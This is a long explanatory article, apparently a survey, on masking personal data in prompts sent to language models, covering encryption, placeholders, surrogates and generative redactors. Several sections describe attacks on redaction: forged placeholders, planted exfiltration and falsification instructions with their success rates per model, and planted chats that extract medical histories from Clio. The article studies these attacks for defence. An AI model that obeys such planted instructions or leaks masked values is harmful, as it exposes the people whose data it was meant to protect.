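Format-preserving encryption replaces a value with another in the same format, and the key alone is enough to recover the original. In an example from Elmahallawy and colleagues, the US social security number 479-13-8850 becomes 790-88-0367, and the phone number +1-202-555-0173 becomes +1-537-144-4801, with the country code unchanged. The placeholders reveal the format and, as long as the key stays the same, which values repeat.

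This kind of encryption is weaker when few values are possible. The US standards agency NIST originally required at least one hundred possible values and recommended a million. After researchers published attacks on small sets, a draft revision required at least a million. NIST's *Methods for Format-Preserving Encryption* (2025) announced a second draft, which requires more possible values for the method called FF1 than the original standard did and drops a related method, FF3, in which a cryptographer had found a weakness.

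Elmahallawy and colleagues use FF1, and their phone and card numbers meet the revised minimum of one million possible values. Their dates meet only the original standard, because the system numbers the 73,049 days from 1900 to 2099 and encrypts each day's number as five digits, which leaves 100,000 possibilities.

Encrypting dates also destroys their order. One test prompt described an article written on 12 August 2014 and updated on 6 January 2017. After encryption, the article dated from 1981 and the update from 1909. The alternative is to shift every date in a document by the same secret number of days, up to 4,000 in either direction. This preserves the intervals between dates but reveals them to the provider. One variant also shifts the current date stated in the prompt, so the model can still tell past from future. However, a provider that knows the real date can compare it with the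 shifted one, work out the offset, and recover every date in the document.

### Prεεmpt's definition of a sanitizer

Roy Chowdhury and colleagues give a formal definition of what such a system must do. A *prompt sanitizer* consists of four algorithms. In the notation used so far, with a secret key $k$ in place of the table, they work like this:

$$k \leftarrow \mathrm{Setup}(), \qquad t = \mathrm{Annotate}(x), \qquad \tilde{x} = \mathrm{Sanitize}(k,t), \qquad y' = \mathrm{Desanitize}(k, f(\tilde{x}))$$

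Setup generates the key. The annotator splits the text into pieces and gives each a type, such as name, age or "not sensitive". Sanitize replaces the sensitive pieces, and Desanitize is meant to undo the replacement in the model's answer. The definition also requires the annotator to find the same types in the same order when run on the masked text. The annotator must therefore still label the replacement for a name as a name, which favours realistic values over bracketed labels.

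Privacy is defined through a game in which the attacker writes two prompts, the system secretly picks one and sanitizes it, and the attacker guesses which it was. Both prompts must give the same output under a *leakage function*, which describes everything the masked text reveals by design. For full redaction of "My age is 26", the leakage is "My age is []". The attacker's advantage is twice the probability of a correct guess, minus one, so random guessing scores 0 and always guessing correctly scores 1.

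Their own system, Prεεmpt, divides sensitive values by what the model needs from them. For names, card numbers and phone numbers it assumes that the answer depends only on the format, and encrypts them. For ages and salaries the size matters, since advice on retirement savings would be useless if 50 became 7. Prεεmpt gives these values random noise that makes nearby results likelier than distant ones. The noise satisfies metric differential privacy: for any two true values $a$ and $a'$ and any set of outputs $O$,

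$$\Pr[N(a) \in O] \le e^{\epsilon |a-a'|}\, \Pr[N(a') \in O]$$

where $N$ is the noise mechanism and a smaller $\epsilon$ means more noise. With $\epsilon = 1$, an attacker who has to choose between the ages 50 and 51, both equally likely beforehand, is right at most 73% of the time. For 50 and 70 the inequality guarantees almost nothing, which is deliberate, because the model needs to know roughly how old the person is.

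The April 2025 version of the paper also states a theorem for the whole system, which bounds the attacker's advantage by $e^{l\epsilon}$ plus a negligible term, where $l$ is the largest difference between paired numbers in the two prompts. This bound is never below 1, and an advantage can't exceed 1, so the theorem as written doesn't limit the attacker. The protection for the numbers comes instead from the inequality for the noise.

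Adding independent noise to linked numbers in a prompt, such as a monthly salary of 1,000 and an annual salary of 12,000, would make them contradict each other. Prεεmpt can instead add noise to the monthly figure and multiply the result by twelve, if someone has specified the relationship. Prεεmpt doesn't store the noise it adds, so it can't remove that noise from an age or salary in the answer.

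Roy Chowdhury and colleagues prefer a key to a table because a table grows with every value, and storing users' details after a session can conflict with their legal right to deletion. But a table can also make deletion easier, because deleting Keller's row makes her random token meaningless wherever copies of it survive. An encrypted phone number in a provider's log stays reversible until the company destroys the key, after which it can't restore anything else encrypted under that key either.

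Because Prεεmpt keeps no table, it decrypts every value of the right type in the answer, so a public helpline number that the model adds from memory becomes some other number. The user can prevent this by supplying the original prompt, so that Prεεmpt restores only values that appeared in it. But then somebody has to keep the prompt, which is at least as sensitive as the table would have been.

### Realistic surrogates

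Elmahallawy and colleagues' system, Veil-then-Reveal, encrypts numbers and full dates but replaces names, places, organisations and email addresses with invented values from pools. To replace Marie Curie, the program puts the name in lower case, computes a keyed hash and uses the result to pick an entry from the pool. If another person in the session already has that entry, the program changes a counter in the hash input and tries again. Marie Curie becomes Ágnes Orosz with one session key and Lucie Musil with another. A table on the user's device links each original value to its replacement.

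The check for duplicates matters because different names can otherwise share a surrogate. When Elmahallawy and colleagues ran Prεεmpt on their own test data for comparison, its name encryption produced 875 such collisions, and only 72.9% of names were restored correctly.

Surrogates can introduce errors. In one test, the program replaced the name Richmond Bowie Deckow with Samantha Leonard, and the model wrote that it would "contact her". Restoration brought back the original name but left the pronoun unchanged. Surrogates also don't always hide the replacement, since only 8.5% of the substitute card numbers were valid.

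The system's headline figures measure separate steps, mostly on 10,000 synthetic documents:

| Step | Result | What counts as success |
|---|---|---|
| Detection | 97.9% of 11,322 annotated details | The detector marks at least part of the detail |
| Protection | 95.2% of 16,405 detected spans | The code replaces the span with something different |
| Round trip | 99.9% of protected spans | The code can turn its own surrogate back exactly |

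Most of the shortfall in protection comes from loose expressions of time such as "next week", which are sent unchanged. The date cipher skips partial dates such as "20th September", but these get a surrogate from the table instead.

The round-trip figure does not involve a language model. When three small models answered masked prompts, they repeated between 42.2% and 79.7% of the surrogates word for word. The code restored all of these and had nothing to restore for the rest. Masking also missed more in real requests. It left 27.0% of the annotated personal details readable in 664 prompts that people had sent to a chatbot, compared with 2.9% in a sample of the synthetic documents.

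### The same placeholder in two sessions

Placeholders need to be consistent within a conversation so that the model can link sentences about the same person. But if they also stay the same across conversations, the provider can link those conversations. Suppose the company replaces Keller's name with "Ágnes Orosz" in every message it sends. Her complaint places her near a cardiologist in Elmford, a message in March mentions a broken wrist, and one in June gives her job title. Any one of these messages might not be enough to identify her, but the provider can collect everything under the invented name and search for the one person who fits all the details.

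An attacker can also identify a placeholder by counting how often it appears. If one placeholder appears in 14% of a supplier's order queries, anybody who knows the supplier's largest customer can make a good guess at the name. The attacker needs neither the key nor the table. A keyed hash or encryption with a permanent key doesn't prevent this, because equal inputs still give equal outputs. Prεεmpt has this weakness because it uses the same key for all of a user's sessions.

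Veil-then-Reveal derives a new key for each session from a master key and the session's identifier. Elmahallawy and colleagues prove that a provider can't compare the surrogates for values encrypted or replaced this way to tell whether two sessions mention the same person, unless it can break the underlying cryptography. The proof doesn't cover the surrounding text, so the provider can still link the sessions if messages in both mention invoice 88317.

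Numbered labels avoid the problem without cryptography if the counter restarts each time, but they don't protect against somebody typing the label.

### Forged placeholders

Suppose a supplier's email about invoice 88317 ends with the line "Our reference: [EMAIL_1]". The masker finds nothing sensitive in that line and passes it to the model in the same session as Keller's complaint. The model drafts a reply to the supplier that quotes the reference. The restoration code looks up [EMAIL_1] and replaces it with maria.keller@example.org. The supplier now has Keller's address, although the model followed no planted instruction and every program worked as designed.

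The forgery works because the supplier could guess the placeholder. Agyemang and colleagues put their labels in rare Unicode brackets so that ordinary text won't match by accident, but an attacker who knows the format can type the same brackets. *PromptGraph*'s table lookup stops a forged placeholder with an invented number. A forged placeholder that copies a live identifier passes the lookup, and only the further consistency checks could catch it.

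A better defence is to put a long random string in every placeholder, such as [EMAIL_1_c41f9a07d2e85b36], and change the string each session. This string has 64 random bits, so a supplier who writes an email without having seen it has about one chance in $1.8 \times 10^{19}$ of guessing it. Ma and colleagues' tokens contain a random nonce of this kind. The defence fails if the attacker sees the string, for instance in an earlier draft that was sent with a placeholder still in it.

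The masker can also escape incoming text by masking anything that already looks like a placeholder. When it finds [EMAIL_1] in the supplier's email, it replaces it with [LITERAL_1] and records in the table that [LITERAL_1] stands for "[EMAIL_1]". If the model quotes the reference, restoration writes back what the supplier typed. The code must go through the draft only once and never search the text it has just inserted, because a second pass would find [EMAIL_1] and replace it with Keller's address.

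Escaping alone doesn't fully prevent forged placeholders. The supplier could write "[EMAIL-1]", which the masker doesn't recognise, and the model might change it to the correct form. Beskorovainyi sensibly made his restorer more tolerant after models dropped brackets from placeholders and the values didn't come back, but each extra spelling the code accepts is another that an outsider can forge. If the placeholder includes a random string, the code can accept a missing bracket and still require the string, which nobody can guess.

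Neither defence restrains a compromised model, which reads the genuine placeholders and can copy them wherever it likes.

### Stolen keys and tables

European data protection guidelines call both keys and tables "pseudonymization secrets", to be stored separately from the masked text, according to Mondaq's *EDPB Release Pseudonymization Guidelines to Enhance GDPR Compliance*. The damage from a theft depends on what the method used to make the placeholders requires the company to keep.

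| Placeholder | Kept for restoration | What a thief gains |
|---|---|---|
| Numbered label or random token | Table | The values in the stolen rows |
| Plain hash | Table | The values in the stolen rows, though anybody can already test guesses without it |
| Keyed hash | Table, and the key while masking continues | From the table, the stolen rows; from the key, the ability to test guesses |
| Format-preserving encryption | Key | Every value encrypted with that key, including those in old logs |
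| Surrogate from a pool | Table, and a key if a keyed hash picks the surrogate | From the table, the stolen rows; from the key, a shortlist of likely names |

Ma and colleagues' simulated attack, mentioned earlier, puts figures on this for random tokens whose sessions all depend on one master seed:

| Attacker's access | Recovered from the targeted session | Recovered from other sessions |
|---|---|---|
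| Tokens only | 0% | 0% |
| Audit log | 0% | 0% |
| Half of the session's table | 50% | 0% |
| Whole table, or the session's credential | 100% | 0% |
| Master seed | 100% | 100% |

This test used a reference design, not a live system, and the results follow closely from the design's assumptions. Reading half the table exposes half its values by definition, and reading the audit log exposes none because the design keeps real values out of it. A deployed system could expose values in ways the design rules out, for example if a debugging log recorded them or if two sessions shared a credential. The figures still show that the master seed needs the most protection in such a system.

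Deleting secrets early also limits what a thief can recover. Ma and colleagues recommend removing expired mappings promptly, and Elmahallawy and colleagues discard both the keys and the table when a session ends. A thief who breaks in the next day finds nothing that can reverse the placeholders in the provider's logs. The company can't reverse them either, so a reply that arrives after the session ends keeps its placeholders permanently.

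## Experiments in which a model writes the redacted text

A company that masks Keller's complaint with code has to guard a table or a key. If it asks a language model to write the redacted version instead, it also has to trust the model with her phone number, because the model works from the original text.

The system prompt for OpenAnonymity's scrubber, reprinted in *Can Prompt Anonymity Protect Your Identity From LLM Providers?* (2026), tells the scrubbing model to rewrite the user's entire prompt before a remote model sees it. The scrubbing model must remove names, account numbers and access keys, as well as catchphrases, emojis and unusual capitals, and it should swap in neutral words where the meaning stays the same. A correct rewrite can therefore differ from the original in almost any word.

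The model's freedom to change words exposes the method to attack, because the model reads any instruction planted in the complaint along with the values it should hide. Code that receives the answer can't distinguish a harmless word swap from one that encodes a digit.

### Four ways to get the complaint wrong

A redactor that writes freely can fail on Keller's message in four ways:

| Failure | What the redacted complaint might contain | Can rule-based substitution do this? |
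|---|---|---|
| A value left in | "[PERSON_1] ([EMAIL_1], 555-0142) disputes invoice 88317" | Yes, if the phone pattern misses the number |
| A value moved or re-expressed | [PHONE_1] in the right place, but the digits spelled out as words in a closing remark | No |
| Other text altered | "disputes invoice 88371" | Only by masking harmless text |
| Text invented | "She has asked for a full refund." | No |

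A phone number that stays in or turns up elsewhere exposes Keller. The wrong invoice number and the made-up refund don't expose anyone, but an employee who reads only the redacted version may act on them. Substitution code avoids most of these errors because it copies everything outside the detected spans.

*PRvL* (Garza, Kotal and colleagues, 2025) gives examples of language models redacting short texts. One model masked the date in a sentence about an email from Jordan but left "Jordan" readable. Another received "Thank you for your interest", which names nobody, and added a name placeholder to the end.

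### What planted instructions achieve

The most relevant attack data come from *When the Spec Sheet Lies* (Watson, Bücheler and Richards, 2026), which tested five language models on six kinds of industrial document task, such as extracting the terms of a supplier's quote or summarising the hazards of a chemical. The researchers either hid a malicious instruction in the source document or appended it to the prompt. A program searched each output for a string that would show the attack had worked. The attack succeeded in 65.1% of 3,000 trials.

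Watson and colleagues tried five kinds of instruction. The most relevant to redaction is "exfiltrate", which is meant to make the model leak information or reveal something it should have redacted. These attacks succeeded in 58% of trials when the instruction was in the document and in 72% when it came at the end of the prompt. The lower figure fits Keller's case better, since an outsider can add a line to a complaint but can't normally edit the company's prompt. However, Watson and colleagues suspect that text near the end of a prompt has more influence. If they are right, an instruction hidden in the complaint would succeed more often when the redactor places the complaint after its own instructions.

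The exfiltration attacks succeeded in 2% of trials against the Claude model and 40% against GPT-4o. If every model had the same number of trials, the other three (Llama 3.1 8B, Mistral 7B and Qwen2.5 7B) must have averaged about 94%. This is a problem for generative redaction, because a company that wants to keep Keller's details away from outside providers has to run the redactor on its own machines, and small open-weight models like these three are the easiest to run there.

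Instructions to falsify a fact worked even better, succeeding in 45% of trials against Claude and in every trial against GPT-4o. Watson and colleagues suggest that a false correction looks like an ordinary request, unlike an order to ignore earlier instructions. A planted line that "corrects" the invoice number in Keller's complaint would be an attack of this type.

A confidential value can move from a source document into text the model writes. In one run, Claude noticed a suspicious section in a supplier's document, and its warning to the human reviewer repeated the confidential reference number from that section.

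These percentages are rough estimates of how often a redactor would leak. Language models drafted the test documents, and people edited them. The exfiltration category mixes failed redaction with other leaks, and in the Claude run above, the confidential number was part of the suspicious section. Watson and colleagues didn't check whether the outputs were correct without an attack, so it is unknown how many confidential details the models would have exposed anyway. The design as described would give 4,500 trials if every combination were run, not the 3,000 reported. The paper also calls the Claude model "Claude 4.6 Sonnet" in one place and "Claude Sonnet 5" in others, so it is unclear which model produced the 2% result.

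An instruction can mislead a redactor even if nobody meant harm. In *Can Large Language Models Really Recognize Your Name?* (2025), Pham, Kairouz and colleagues studied Clio, which Anthropic uses to summarise what people ask its chatbot. A model in Clio reads each conversation and writes a short description meant to leave out personal details. Pham and colleagues gave it text containing real but unusual names, each one letter away from the name of something else, such as a place, company or mineral. When the text also contained an instruction for some other model, such as a request to keep a certain word intact, Clio was up to four times more likely to leave the name in. Keller could cause the same error by asking the company to spell her name exactly as she does.

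Deliberate attacks on Clio also work, at least in a laboratory. In *CLIOPATRA*, Annamalai, De Cristofaro and Kairouz (2026) planted chats in a local copy and extracted the medical history from up to 65% of the synthetic chats they targeted, although the system has one model to remove personal details and another to audit the summaries. Anthropic acknowledged the risk and later reported that outside testers had failed to re-identify any user of the real system. Annamalai and colleagues object that the outside audit didn't cover an attacker who plants conversations.

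None of these studies, and apparently no other published study, ran rule-based substitution on the same attacked documents. Planted instructions have no effect on regular expressions, but a direct comparison would still be useful because it would measure both methods' errors on the same scale. Regular expressions miss the mention of the cardiologist every time, even without an attack. A generative redactor might usually hide that mention but occasionally leave the phone number readable.

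### Errors that nobody provoked

Models also garble text that nobody has tampered with. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) suggests a possible cause. It describes a filter model meant to delete planted instructions and repeat the rest of the text. In early experiments, the model sometimes deleted the instruction and then made up a continuation, because its original training had taught it to predict plausible next words, not to copy. The developers added training examples that break off abruptly to teach the model to stop where its input stops.

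Hospital records provide the best evidence on how often this happens in redaction. In the comparison of UK records by Kuo and colleagues, Gemma-7b not only invented an old injury but also translated records into other languages and added treatment advice. All of its outputs that the researchers inspected contained invented content. Llama-3-8B mostly erred by removing too much. With five worked examples in its prompt, it caught 99% of the identifying words, but only about 8% of the words it redacted were identifying. Llama-3-8B and Phi-3 also added remarks about the task, despite being told not to output any additional text. The researchers saw no such remarks once the prompt contained ten examples.

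Kuo and colleagues saw no invented text from GPT-4, GPT-3.5 or the four specialised tools, but they read only 50 outputs per model and prompt setting. That result is compatible with a true rate of up to about 6%. The language models date from early 2024, so the results probably understate what current ones can do.

Kuo and colleagues used BLEU, a score from machine translation research, to assess the records they didn't read. It measures how many runs of one to four words two texts share, and identical texts score 1. The clinicians' own redactions scored 0.931 against the originals, since even perfect redaction removes some words. GPT-4 scored between 0.920 and 0.925, and Gemma-7b never exceeded 0.071.

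In *Harnessing Moderate-Sized Language Models for Reliable Patient Data Deidentification*, Dorémus, Russon and colleagues (2025) used the same score for nurses' notes from the emergency department in Bordeaux. They trained three open models to copy each note, replacing identifying details with "[XXXXX]". If a note contained none, the model was to write only "ANONYMOUS" instead of copying the note. The best model, Mistral 7B, left identifying details in 63 of 3,000 test notes. For 29 of the 63, it had wrongly written "ANONYMOUS". Most of the failures involved names of places and institutions, and the model missed only one patient's name.

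BLEU stayed above 0.9864 after the fifth round of training, and Dorémus and colleagues conclude that the models did not alter the text significantly. But an average of 0.9864 still allows for one wrong word in about two notes out of five. The notes average 439 characters, or roughly 75 words, and one wrong word in the middle of a text that long lowers BLEU from 1 to about 0.966. Missed identifiers probably explain part of the gap between 0.9864 and 1, but how much can't be determined from the score. BLEU also penalizes "left" in place of "right" only as much as a harmless synonym.

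In *Not What the Doctor Ordered* (Aghakasiri, Zambare and colleagues, 2025), a physician and a computer scientist reviewed 500 wrong redactions for each tool and collection of records to see what information was lost. In referral letters to rheumatologists, 89 of Llama 3.3's 500 wrong redactions removed clinically relevant information, and physicians rated 67 of these as serious. The figures for two tools that only label words were 22 and 14.

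Llama 3.3 made far fewer wrong redactions in the letters than the other two tools did, with 2,404 against 18,485 and 29,609. If the samples are representative, it removed about 430 clinically relevant words, while each of the others removed more than 800. On American discharge summaries, though, the labelling tool ClinicalBERT removed only about a third as many relevant words as Llama, perhaps because its developers had trained it on records from the same collection. Removing too much is therefore not a weakness specific to generative redaction. The review covered only wrong redactions, so it would not have counted a sentence that a model invented.

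More recent models copy better, but they still make mistakes in long documents. In *LLMs Corrupt Your Documents When You Delegate*, Laban, Schnabel and Neville (2026) had 19 models make a complicated edit and then reverse it, for example by splitting a ledger into categories and merging it again. After one pair of edits, Gemini 3.1 Pro preserved 96.8% of the content by their measure and Claude 4.6 Opus 94.2%. After ten pairs, the three best models had lost an average of a quarter of the content. Redaction is one much simpler edit, so its error rate should be far lower. But the errors that Laban and colleagues describe are few and severe, in documents that otherwise look fine, and people who use a model to redact would want to know about errors like these.

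### Comparing the output with the source

Such errors are hard to notice because the result reads well. *AI health literacy as a foundation for responsible AI in healthcare* makes this point about medical text in general, and cites a review that found invented information in 1.47% of 12,999 sentences from model-written clinical notes. Redaction makes errors even harder to notice because the person who reads the redacted complaint usually isn't allowed to compare it with the original.

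Software can make the comparison before release, but an overall similarity score is a poor way to do it. Among the models that Garza and colleagues tested, a version of T5 had the highest score for single words shared with the correct redaction, but it left twelve times as much personal data readable as the best model. Aghakasiri and colleagues tested a published measure that predicts diagnosis codes from a note before and after redaction and counts the differences. Its correlation with the clinicians' judgement was 0.04 on the discharge summaries and negative on the letters.

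The paper's own method lines up the source and the output, cuts both into short pieces, and uses a Llama model to judge whether each pair differs in a clinically meaningful way. The correlation rose to 0.40 on the discharge summaries and 0.78 on the letters. The method helps with accidental mistakes but is weaker against an attacker, because the checking model also reads the original text and any instruction planted there.

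Code can check the output exactly if the redactor may only replace spans with placeholders. The code splits the output at each placeholder and requires the remaining pieces to match the source word for word, in the same order, with gaps only where the placeholders are. Invoice 88371, the invented refund and the spelled-out phone number all fail this check. A phone number left unmasked passes because it matches the source. A redaction that masks half the complaint also passes, though code can count the masked words.

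A model whose output has to pass this check can choose only which spans to mask and which labels to use. It could just as well list the spans and have code write the redacted text, as in *RedactionBench*. A compromised model could still send a signal through its choice of harmless words to mask.

*Integrating a Large Language Model to Streamline Nursing Handover Documentation* describes a similar division of labour, adopted after a failure. A system for Taiwanese hospitals used a model to arrange patients' vital signs, and the model sometimes produced an average body temperature that nobody had recorded. Stricter prompts and review by nurses did not reduce the risk enough for the developers, so they stopped using the model for vital signs. The system now displays the recorded values directly.

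### What a rewriting model does better

The exact check also rejects the best edit a generative redactor can make, which is to replace an identifying detail with a more general one. If a detector found "the only cardiologist in Elmford" and the phrase were deleted, a reader wouldn't know who agreed with Keller. A model can instead write "Her manager, a doctor, agrees", which keeps the sense and no longer singles anyone out. *Stop Tracking Me! Proactive Defense Against Attribute Inference Attack in LLMs* (2026) uses a prompt that asks for edits of this kind. The prompt allows the model to generalise but not to invent, so the model may change "my husband and I" to "my partner and I" but not to "my wife and I".

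*RedacBench* (2026), a benchmark for redaction by language models, makes the same case by pointing to the faults of existing methods, which often miss information that is sensitive because of its meaning, or remove too much. Language models are good at such judgements. In *RedactionBench*, the best models scored 0.81 on 48 documents for which human volunteers averaged 0.77. But code made the replacements in that test, so the result is better evidence for letting a model choose the spans than for letting it write the redacted text.

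Stronger models also resist planted instructions much better, with attack success rates of 2% versus roughly 94% in the Watson study. A strong model may be enough for a company worried only about an occasional stray instruction, but repeated attempts raise an attacker's chance of success. If each attempt has an independent 2% chance of success, someone who sends 50 complaints has about a 64% chance of succeeding at least once. Attackers can also learn from failure. In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) tested a model that rewrites incoming text to remove planted instructions. It stopped every attack in a standard benchmark but let through 30% of deceptive attacks adapted to the defence.

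A company can also use both methods in sequence. Code first masks Keller's name, email address and phone number, and a local model then generalises the phrase about the cardiologist. Even if a line planted in the text takes over the model, the model can't reveal the three masked values because it never received them. Generalising the phrase about the cardiologist still depends on the model working as intended. The model may damage placeholders when it rewrites the text, but code can detect this by searching for exact matches to placeholders such as [PERSON_1].

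## What fixed patterns miss, and what adding a trained detector changes

Code replaces only the spans that a detector finds. If Keller's complaint had also named a colleague, Tomas Brandt, the masking program would have sent his name to the model, because he isn't on the customer's record and a name has no fixed format. The containment argument would still hold for the replaced values, but it wouldn't cover his name. Agyemang and colleagues say that the privacy guarantee of redaction equals the detector's recall, the share of sensitive spans it finds. This dependence on recall is the most serious objection to rule-based substitution, because patterns miss names, trade secrets and descriptions such as "the only cardiologist in Elmford".

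### The reference on the résumé

Yashwant and colleagues measured this gap with 100 synthetic résumés for a warehouse job. Each résumé contains nine details to hide: the applicant's first name, last name, email address, phone number, street address, ZIP code and date of birth, plus the name and phone number of one reference. A detail counts as caught if it no longer appears as a whole word in the masked text. They also checked whether 600 useful terms, such as "forklift operation", remained after masking.

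All four designs search for the applicant's name, which the system already knows. One adds only patterns. Another uses Presidio, Microsoft's free detection library, with a trained language model from spaCy. The other two are hybrids that use a trained detector only for names and patterns for the other details. The faster hybrid calls spaCy's name recogniser directly and switches off spaCy's other language processing.

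| Design | Details caught | Median time per résumé | Time to load |
|---|---|---|---|
| Patterns only | 88.9% | 0.20 ms | 0.8 ms |
| Presidio | 100% | 37.59 ms | 5,021 ms |
| Presidio for names, patterns for the rest | 100% | 30.23 ms | 1,417 ms |
| spaCy's recogniser for names, patterns for the rest | 100% | 13.48 ms | 1,699 ms |

All four designs kept every useful term. The pattern design missed only the reference's name on each résumé, 100 details in all. It hid the reference's phone number, but a name with a job title and an employer is often enough to find someone.

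The 88.9% is eight details out of nine, so it depends on the template. With two references per résumé, the same program would catch nine details out of eleven, or 82%. Two of the eight are caught by looking up the applicant's name, so patterns alone would have caught only 600 of the 900 details. The pattern design exposed somebody in every résumé.

The perfect scores warrant just as much caution, because the generator picked each reference from a list of five names. The recogniser had to find only those five, in nearly identical lines. It also marked "jack" in "pallet jack" as a person, and the researchers added a list of words that cancel a name match. If "jack" is on that list, the name of a reference called Jack would stay readable. Yashwant and colleagues expect every design to miss some details in messier text.

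Speed is a weak reason to leave the recogniser out. The language model that receives the résumé takes a median of 9,120 ms, so even Presidio adds only 0.41% to the wait. The recogniser loads once per process, so loading time matters mainly for services that often start new processes.

### Formats that somebody has to write down

Agyemang and colleagues used a more varied set of 1,300 synthetic prompts with 4,014 labelled details. Their patterns caught every email address, IP address and AWS access key, but missed every personal name, organisation, street address, social security number, employee ID and password.

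These misses are easier to fix when the missed item has a fixed format. A US social security number has three, two and four digits, and the résumé program includes a pattern for it. Employee IDs usually have a fixed format too, which the employer knows, but no pattern describes all personal names. Adding Presidio cut the share of missed names to 12.3% and of missed organisations to 25.9%, but 79.8% of employee IDs still got through. A general-purpose recogniser doesn't come with each company's ID format, but adding a pattern for that format might catch most of these IDs.

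Neither method gives much protection to the 200 prompts that identify somebody by description. With patterns alone, every identifying phrase stayed at least partly readable. With Presidio, 95.0% did, and having a local model rephrase the result lowered that only to 94.1%. This measure is strict, because any four consecutive characters of a phrase count as a partial leak. Presidio left only 11.4% of the phrases fully intact, and a phrase that has lost a company name may no longer identify anyone. The real exposure is probably between 11.4% and 95.0%.

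The lowest leak rates came from sending fewer prompts to the cloud. A small local model answered the easy requests, including 94% of requests in the set full of ordinary personal details. With the rest redacted and rephrased, only 0.6% of the details in that set leaked at least partly. For proprietary code, where the local model could answer only 38% of requests, the same leak rate was 31.3%.

### Why patterns win on one test set and lose on another

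Ma and colleagues compared detectors on 300 synthetic documents with labelled personal details, taken from AI4Privacy, and 493 records of AI agents at work, taken from PrivacyLens. In one such record, an agent might read messages and then write an email. *Residual exposure* is the share of sensitive values still readable after masking.

| Method | Residual exposure, AI4Privacy | Harmless text kept | Residual exposure, PrivacyLens | Harmless text kept |
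|---|---|---|---|---|
| Regular expressions | 67.4% | 98% | 11.8% | 99% |
| Presidio | 52.2% | 97% | 8.9% | 93% |
| 8B language model rewriting the text | 22.1% | 94% | 60.3% | 93% |
| Learned detector | 7.4% | 80% | 1.8% | 75% |

The rewriting model, which has about eight billion parameters, left a third as much sensitive data exposed as the regular expressions did on AI4Privacy, but five times as much on PrivacyLens. The results differ largely because the two collections contain different kinds of sensitive values. AI4Privacy has many kinds, including usernames, passport numbers and parts of addresses, and the regular expressions cover only some of them. A language model can often recognise a username from the sentence around it. The scored values in PrivacyLens are mostly names and email addresses in regular formats, which the regular expressions match wherever they occur.

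This explains why patterns do well on PrivacyLens but not why the language model does so badly. Ma and colleagues identify free-form rewriting as the weakness but don't test the cause. The model may treat an email address in an agent's log as something needed to send the message instead of as a private detail. A regular expression can't make this mistake because it matches the address by its format, without judging its purpose.

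The learned detector did best in both columns. It is a logistic regression, a simple statistical classifier rather than a language model, and it scores each word by its spelling, shape and neighbours. Its exposure is low partly because it masks too much. On the full AI4Privacy test set, it found 95% of the sensitive spans, but only 36% of the spans it marked were labelled as sensitive.

Over-masking makes the text less useful to the next reader. A 32B agent's helpfulness score fell from 2.42 out of 3 with unmasked text to 2.21 with text masked this way. The score of a 70B agent from another model family fell from 2.46 to 1.40.

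The detector also had an advantage on AI4Privacy, because its training documents came from the same collection. It transferred well to clinical notes, where it left 6.1% of the values exposed, but a version trained on clinical notes left 75.4% of the AI4Privacy values exposed. A company therefore needs to test a detector on its own text before relying on figures like these.

### Secrets without a format

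Some secrets never appear as a single string. A few sentences about a supplier, a deadline and a test failure can reveal an unannounced product without naming it. In *Operationalizing the Motivated Intruder*, Grötzner and Tippe argue that protecting such secrets requires inference by a language model, and their results are the best evidence against relying on fixed patterns.

Their gateway gives a model the user's prompt and a written codebook based on European data protection law and Germany's trade secrets act. The model must assume a "motivated intruder", a competent person who searches the internet and public records to work out who or what the prompt is about. If it estimates that fewer than five real people or organisations fit a description, it must change the description. It drops details that the request doesn't need, replaces others with consistent fictional details or more general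 terms, and blanks out text only as a last resort.

Grötzner and Tippe tested the gateway on 127 prompts against Presidio with its default settings:

| Kind of information | Neutralised by the gateway | Neutralised by Presidio |
|---|---|---|
| Personal identifiers stated outright | 100% | 52.6% |
| Trade secrets stated outright, such as project names | 97.6% | 28.8% |
| Trade secrets that emerge from context | 89.9% | 3.1% |

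Presidio also damaged harmless text. It turned the Python expression `io.BytesIO` into `<URL>tesIO` and masked the names of peoples and places in a history question about the Mongol invasions.

The choice of baseline explains part of the gap. Presidio's default settings contain no list of a company's projects and no pattern for its employee IDs, so a company that added both would raise the 28.8%. The list would still miss any project named since its last update. The 3.1% would hardly change, because a list can't match a secret that a reader has to piece together from several sentences.

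The scoring relied partly on Gemini 2.5 Pro, which also ran the gateway, but a human expert labelled every test prompt and a second expert reviewed the disagreements. On 27 harder prompts, such as long career histories, the gateway removed 81.6% of the risks to personal identity.

One of the published successes is questionable, though. The prompt mentioned a project called "OnionAnatomy" along with the anonymity networks Tor and I2P. The model inferred the project's subject and renamed it "DarknetMediaAnalysis", which reveals more to an outsider than the original name did.

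The gateway took an average of 14.24 seconds per prompt, compared with 0.03 seconds for Presidio. Human reviewers judged that the gateway severely damaged 18.1% of the final answers, compared with 22.1% for Presidio. But on prompts dense with personal details, the gateway's rate was 28% and Presidio's was 16%. In one support request, the gateway changed the software's name but kept the error code, which meant nothing without the name.

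The gateway is supposed to run on the user's own hardware. Grötzner and Tippe tried three local models, all with 12 billion parameters or fewer, but none could follow the codebook reliably. They used Gemini 2.5 Pro as a stand-in, which in real use would send the unmasked text to an outside provider. They picked the local models in June 2025, so newer ones may well do better.

They also set prompt injection aside, arguing that users have no reason to undermine their own privacy. That is reasonable when a user types the prompt, but an outsider wrote Keller's complaint. The gateway resisted commands to ignore all previous instructions, but Watson and colleagues found that instructions disguised as ordinary corrections worked better than such commands. Grötzner and Tippe accept that a system may have to prioritize deterministic redaction where the law demands strict secrecy, as with patient records.

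*RedacBench* tests a similar ability on 514 real texts, mostly emails from the energy company Enron. Each text comes with security policies, such as a rule to keep strategic business plans secret, and with short statements that a reader could infer from the text. The benchmark separately measures the share of forbidden statements that a reader can no longer infer after redaction and the share of harmless statements that survive.

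| Redaction | Forbidden statements removed | Harmless statements kept |
|---|---|---|
| Masking, eleven models | 35.9–51.6% | 72.8–85.1% |
| GPT-5-mini, two rounds of rewriting | 80.9% | 37.6% |
| Qwen3-4B, two rounds of rewriting | 75.8% | 44.4% |
| The researchers, by hand | 62.8% | 85.2% |
| The researchers, by hand, more strictly | 72.6% | 57.5% |

The masking row is weak evidence about rule-based substitution, because a language model does this masking too. It receives an instruction to mask and writes out the whole text. In one published sample, it also changed "the west desk" to "the team", which substitution code would not do.

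The percentages also depend heavily on which model judges the text. GPT-4.1's masked texts score 36.4% for removal when GPT-4.1-mini decides what a reader could infer, and 86.6% when GPT-5 does. The methods rank in the same order whichever model judges, so the comparison between rewriting and masking is more reliable than any single score. Even the researchers, working by hand, had to give up a lot of harmless content to remove more of the forbidden statements.

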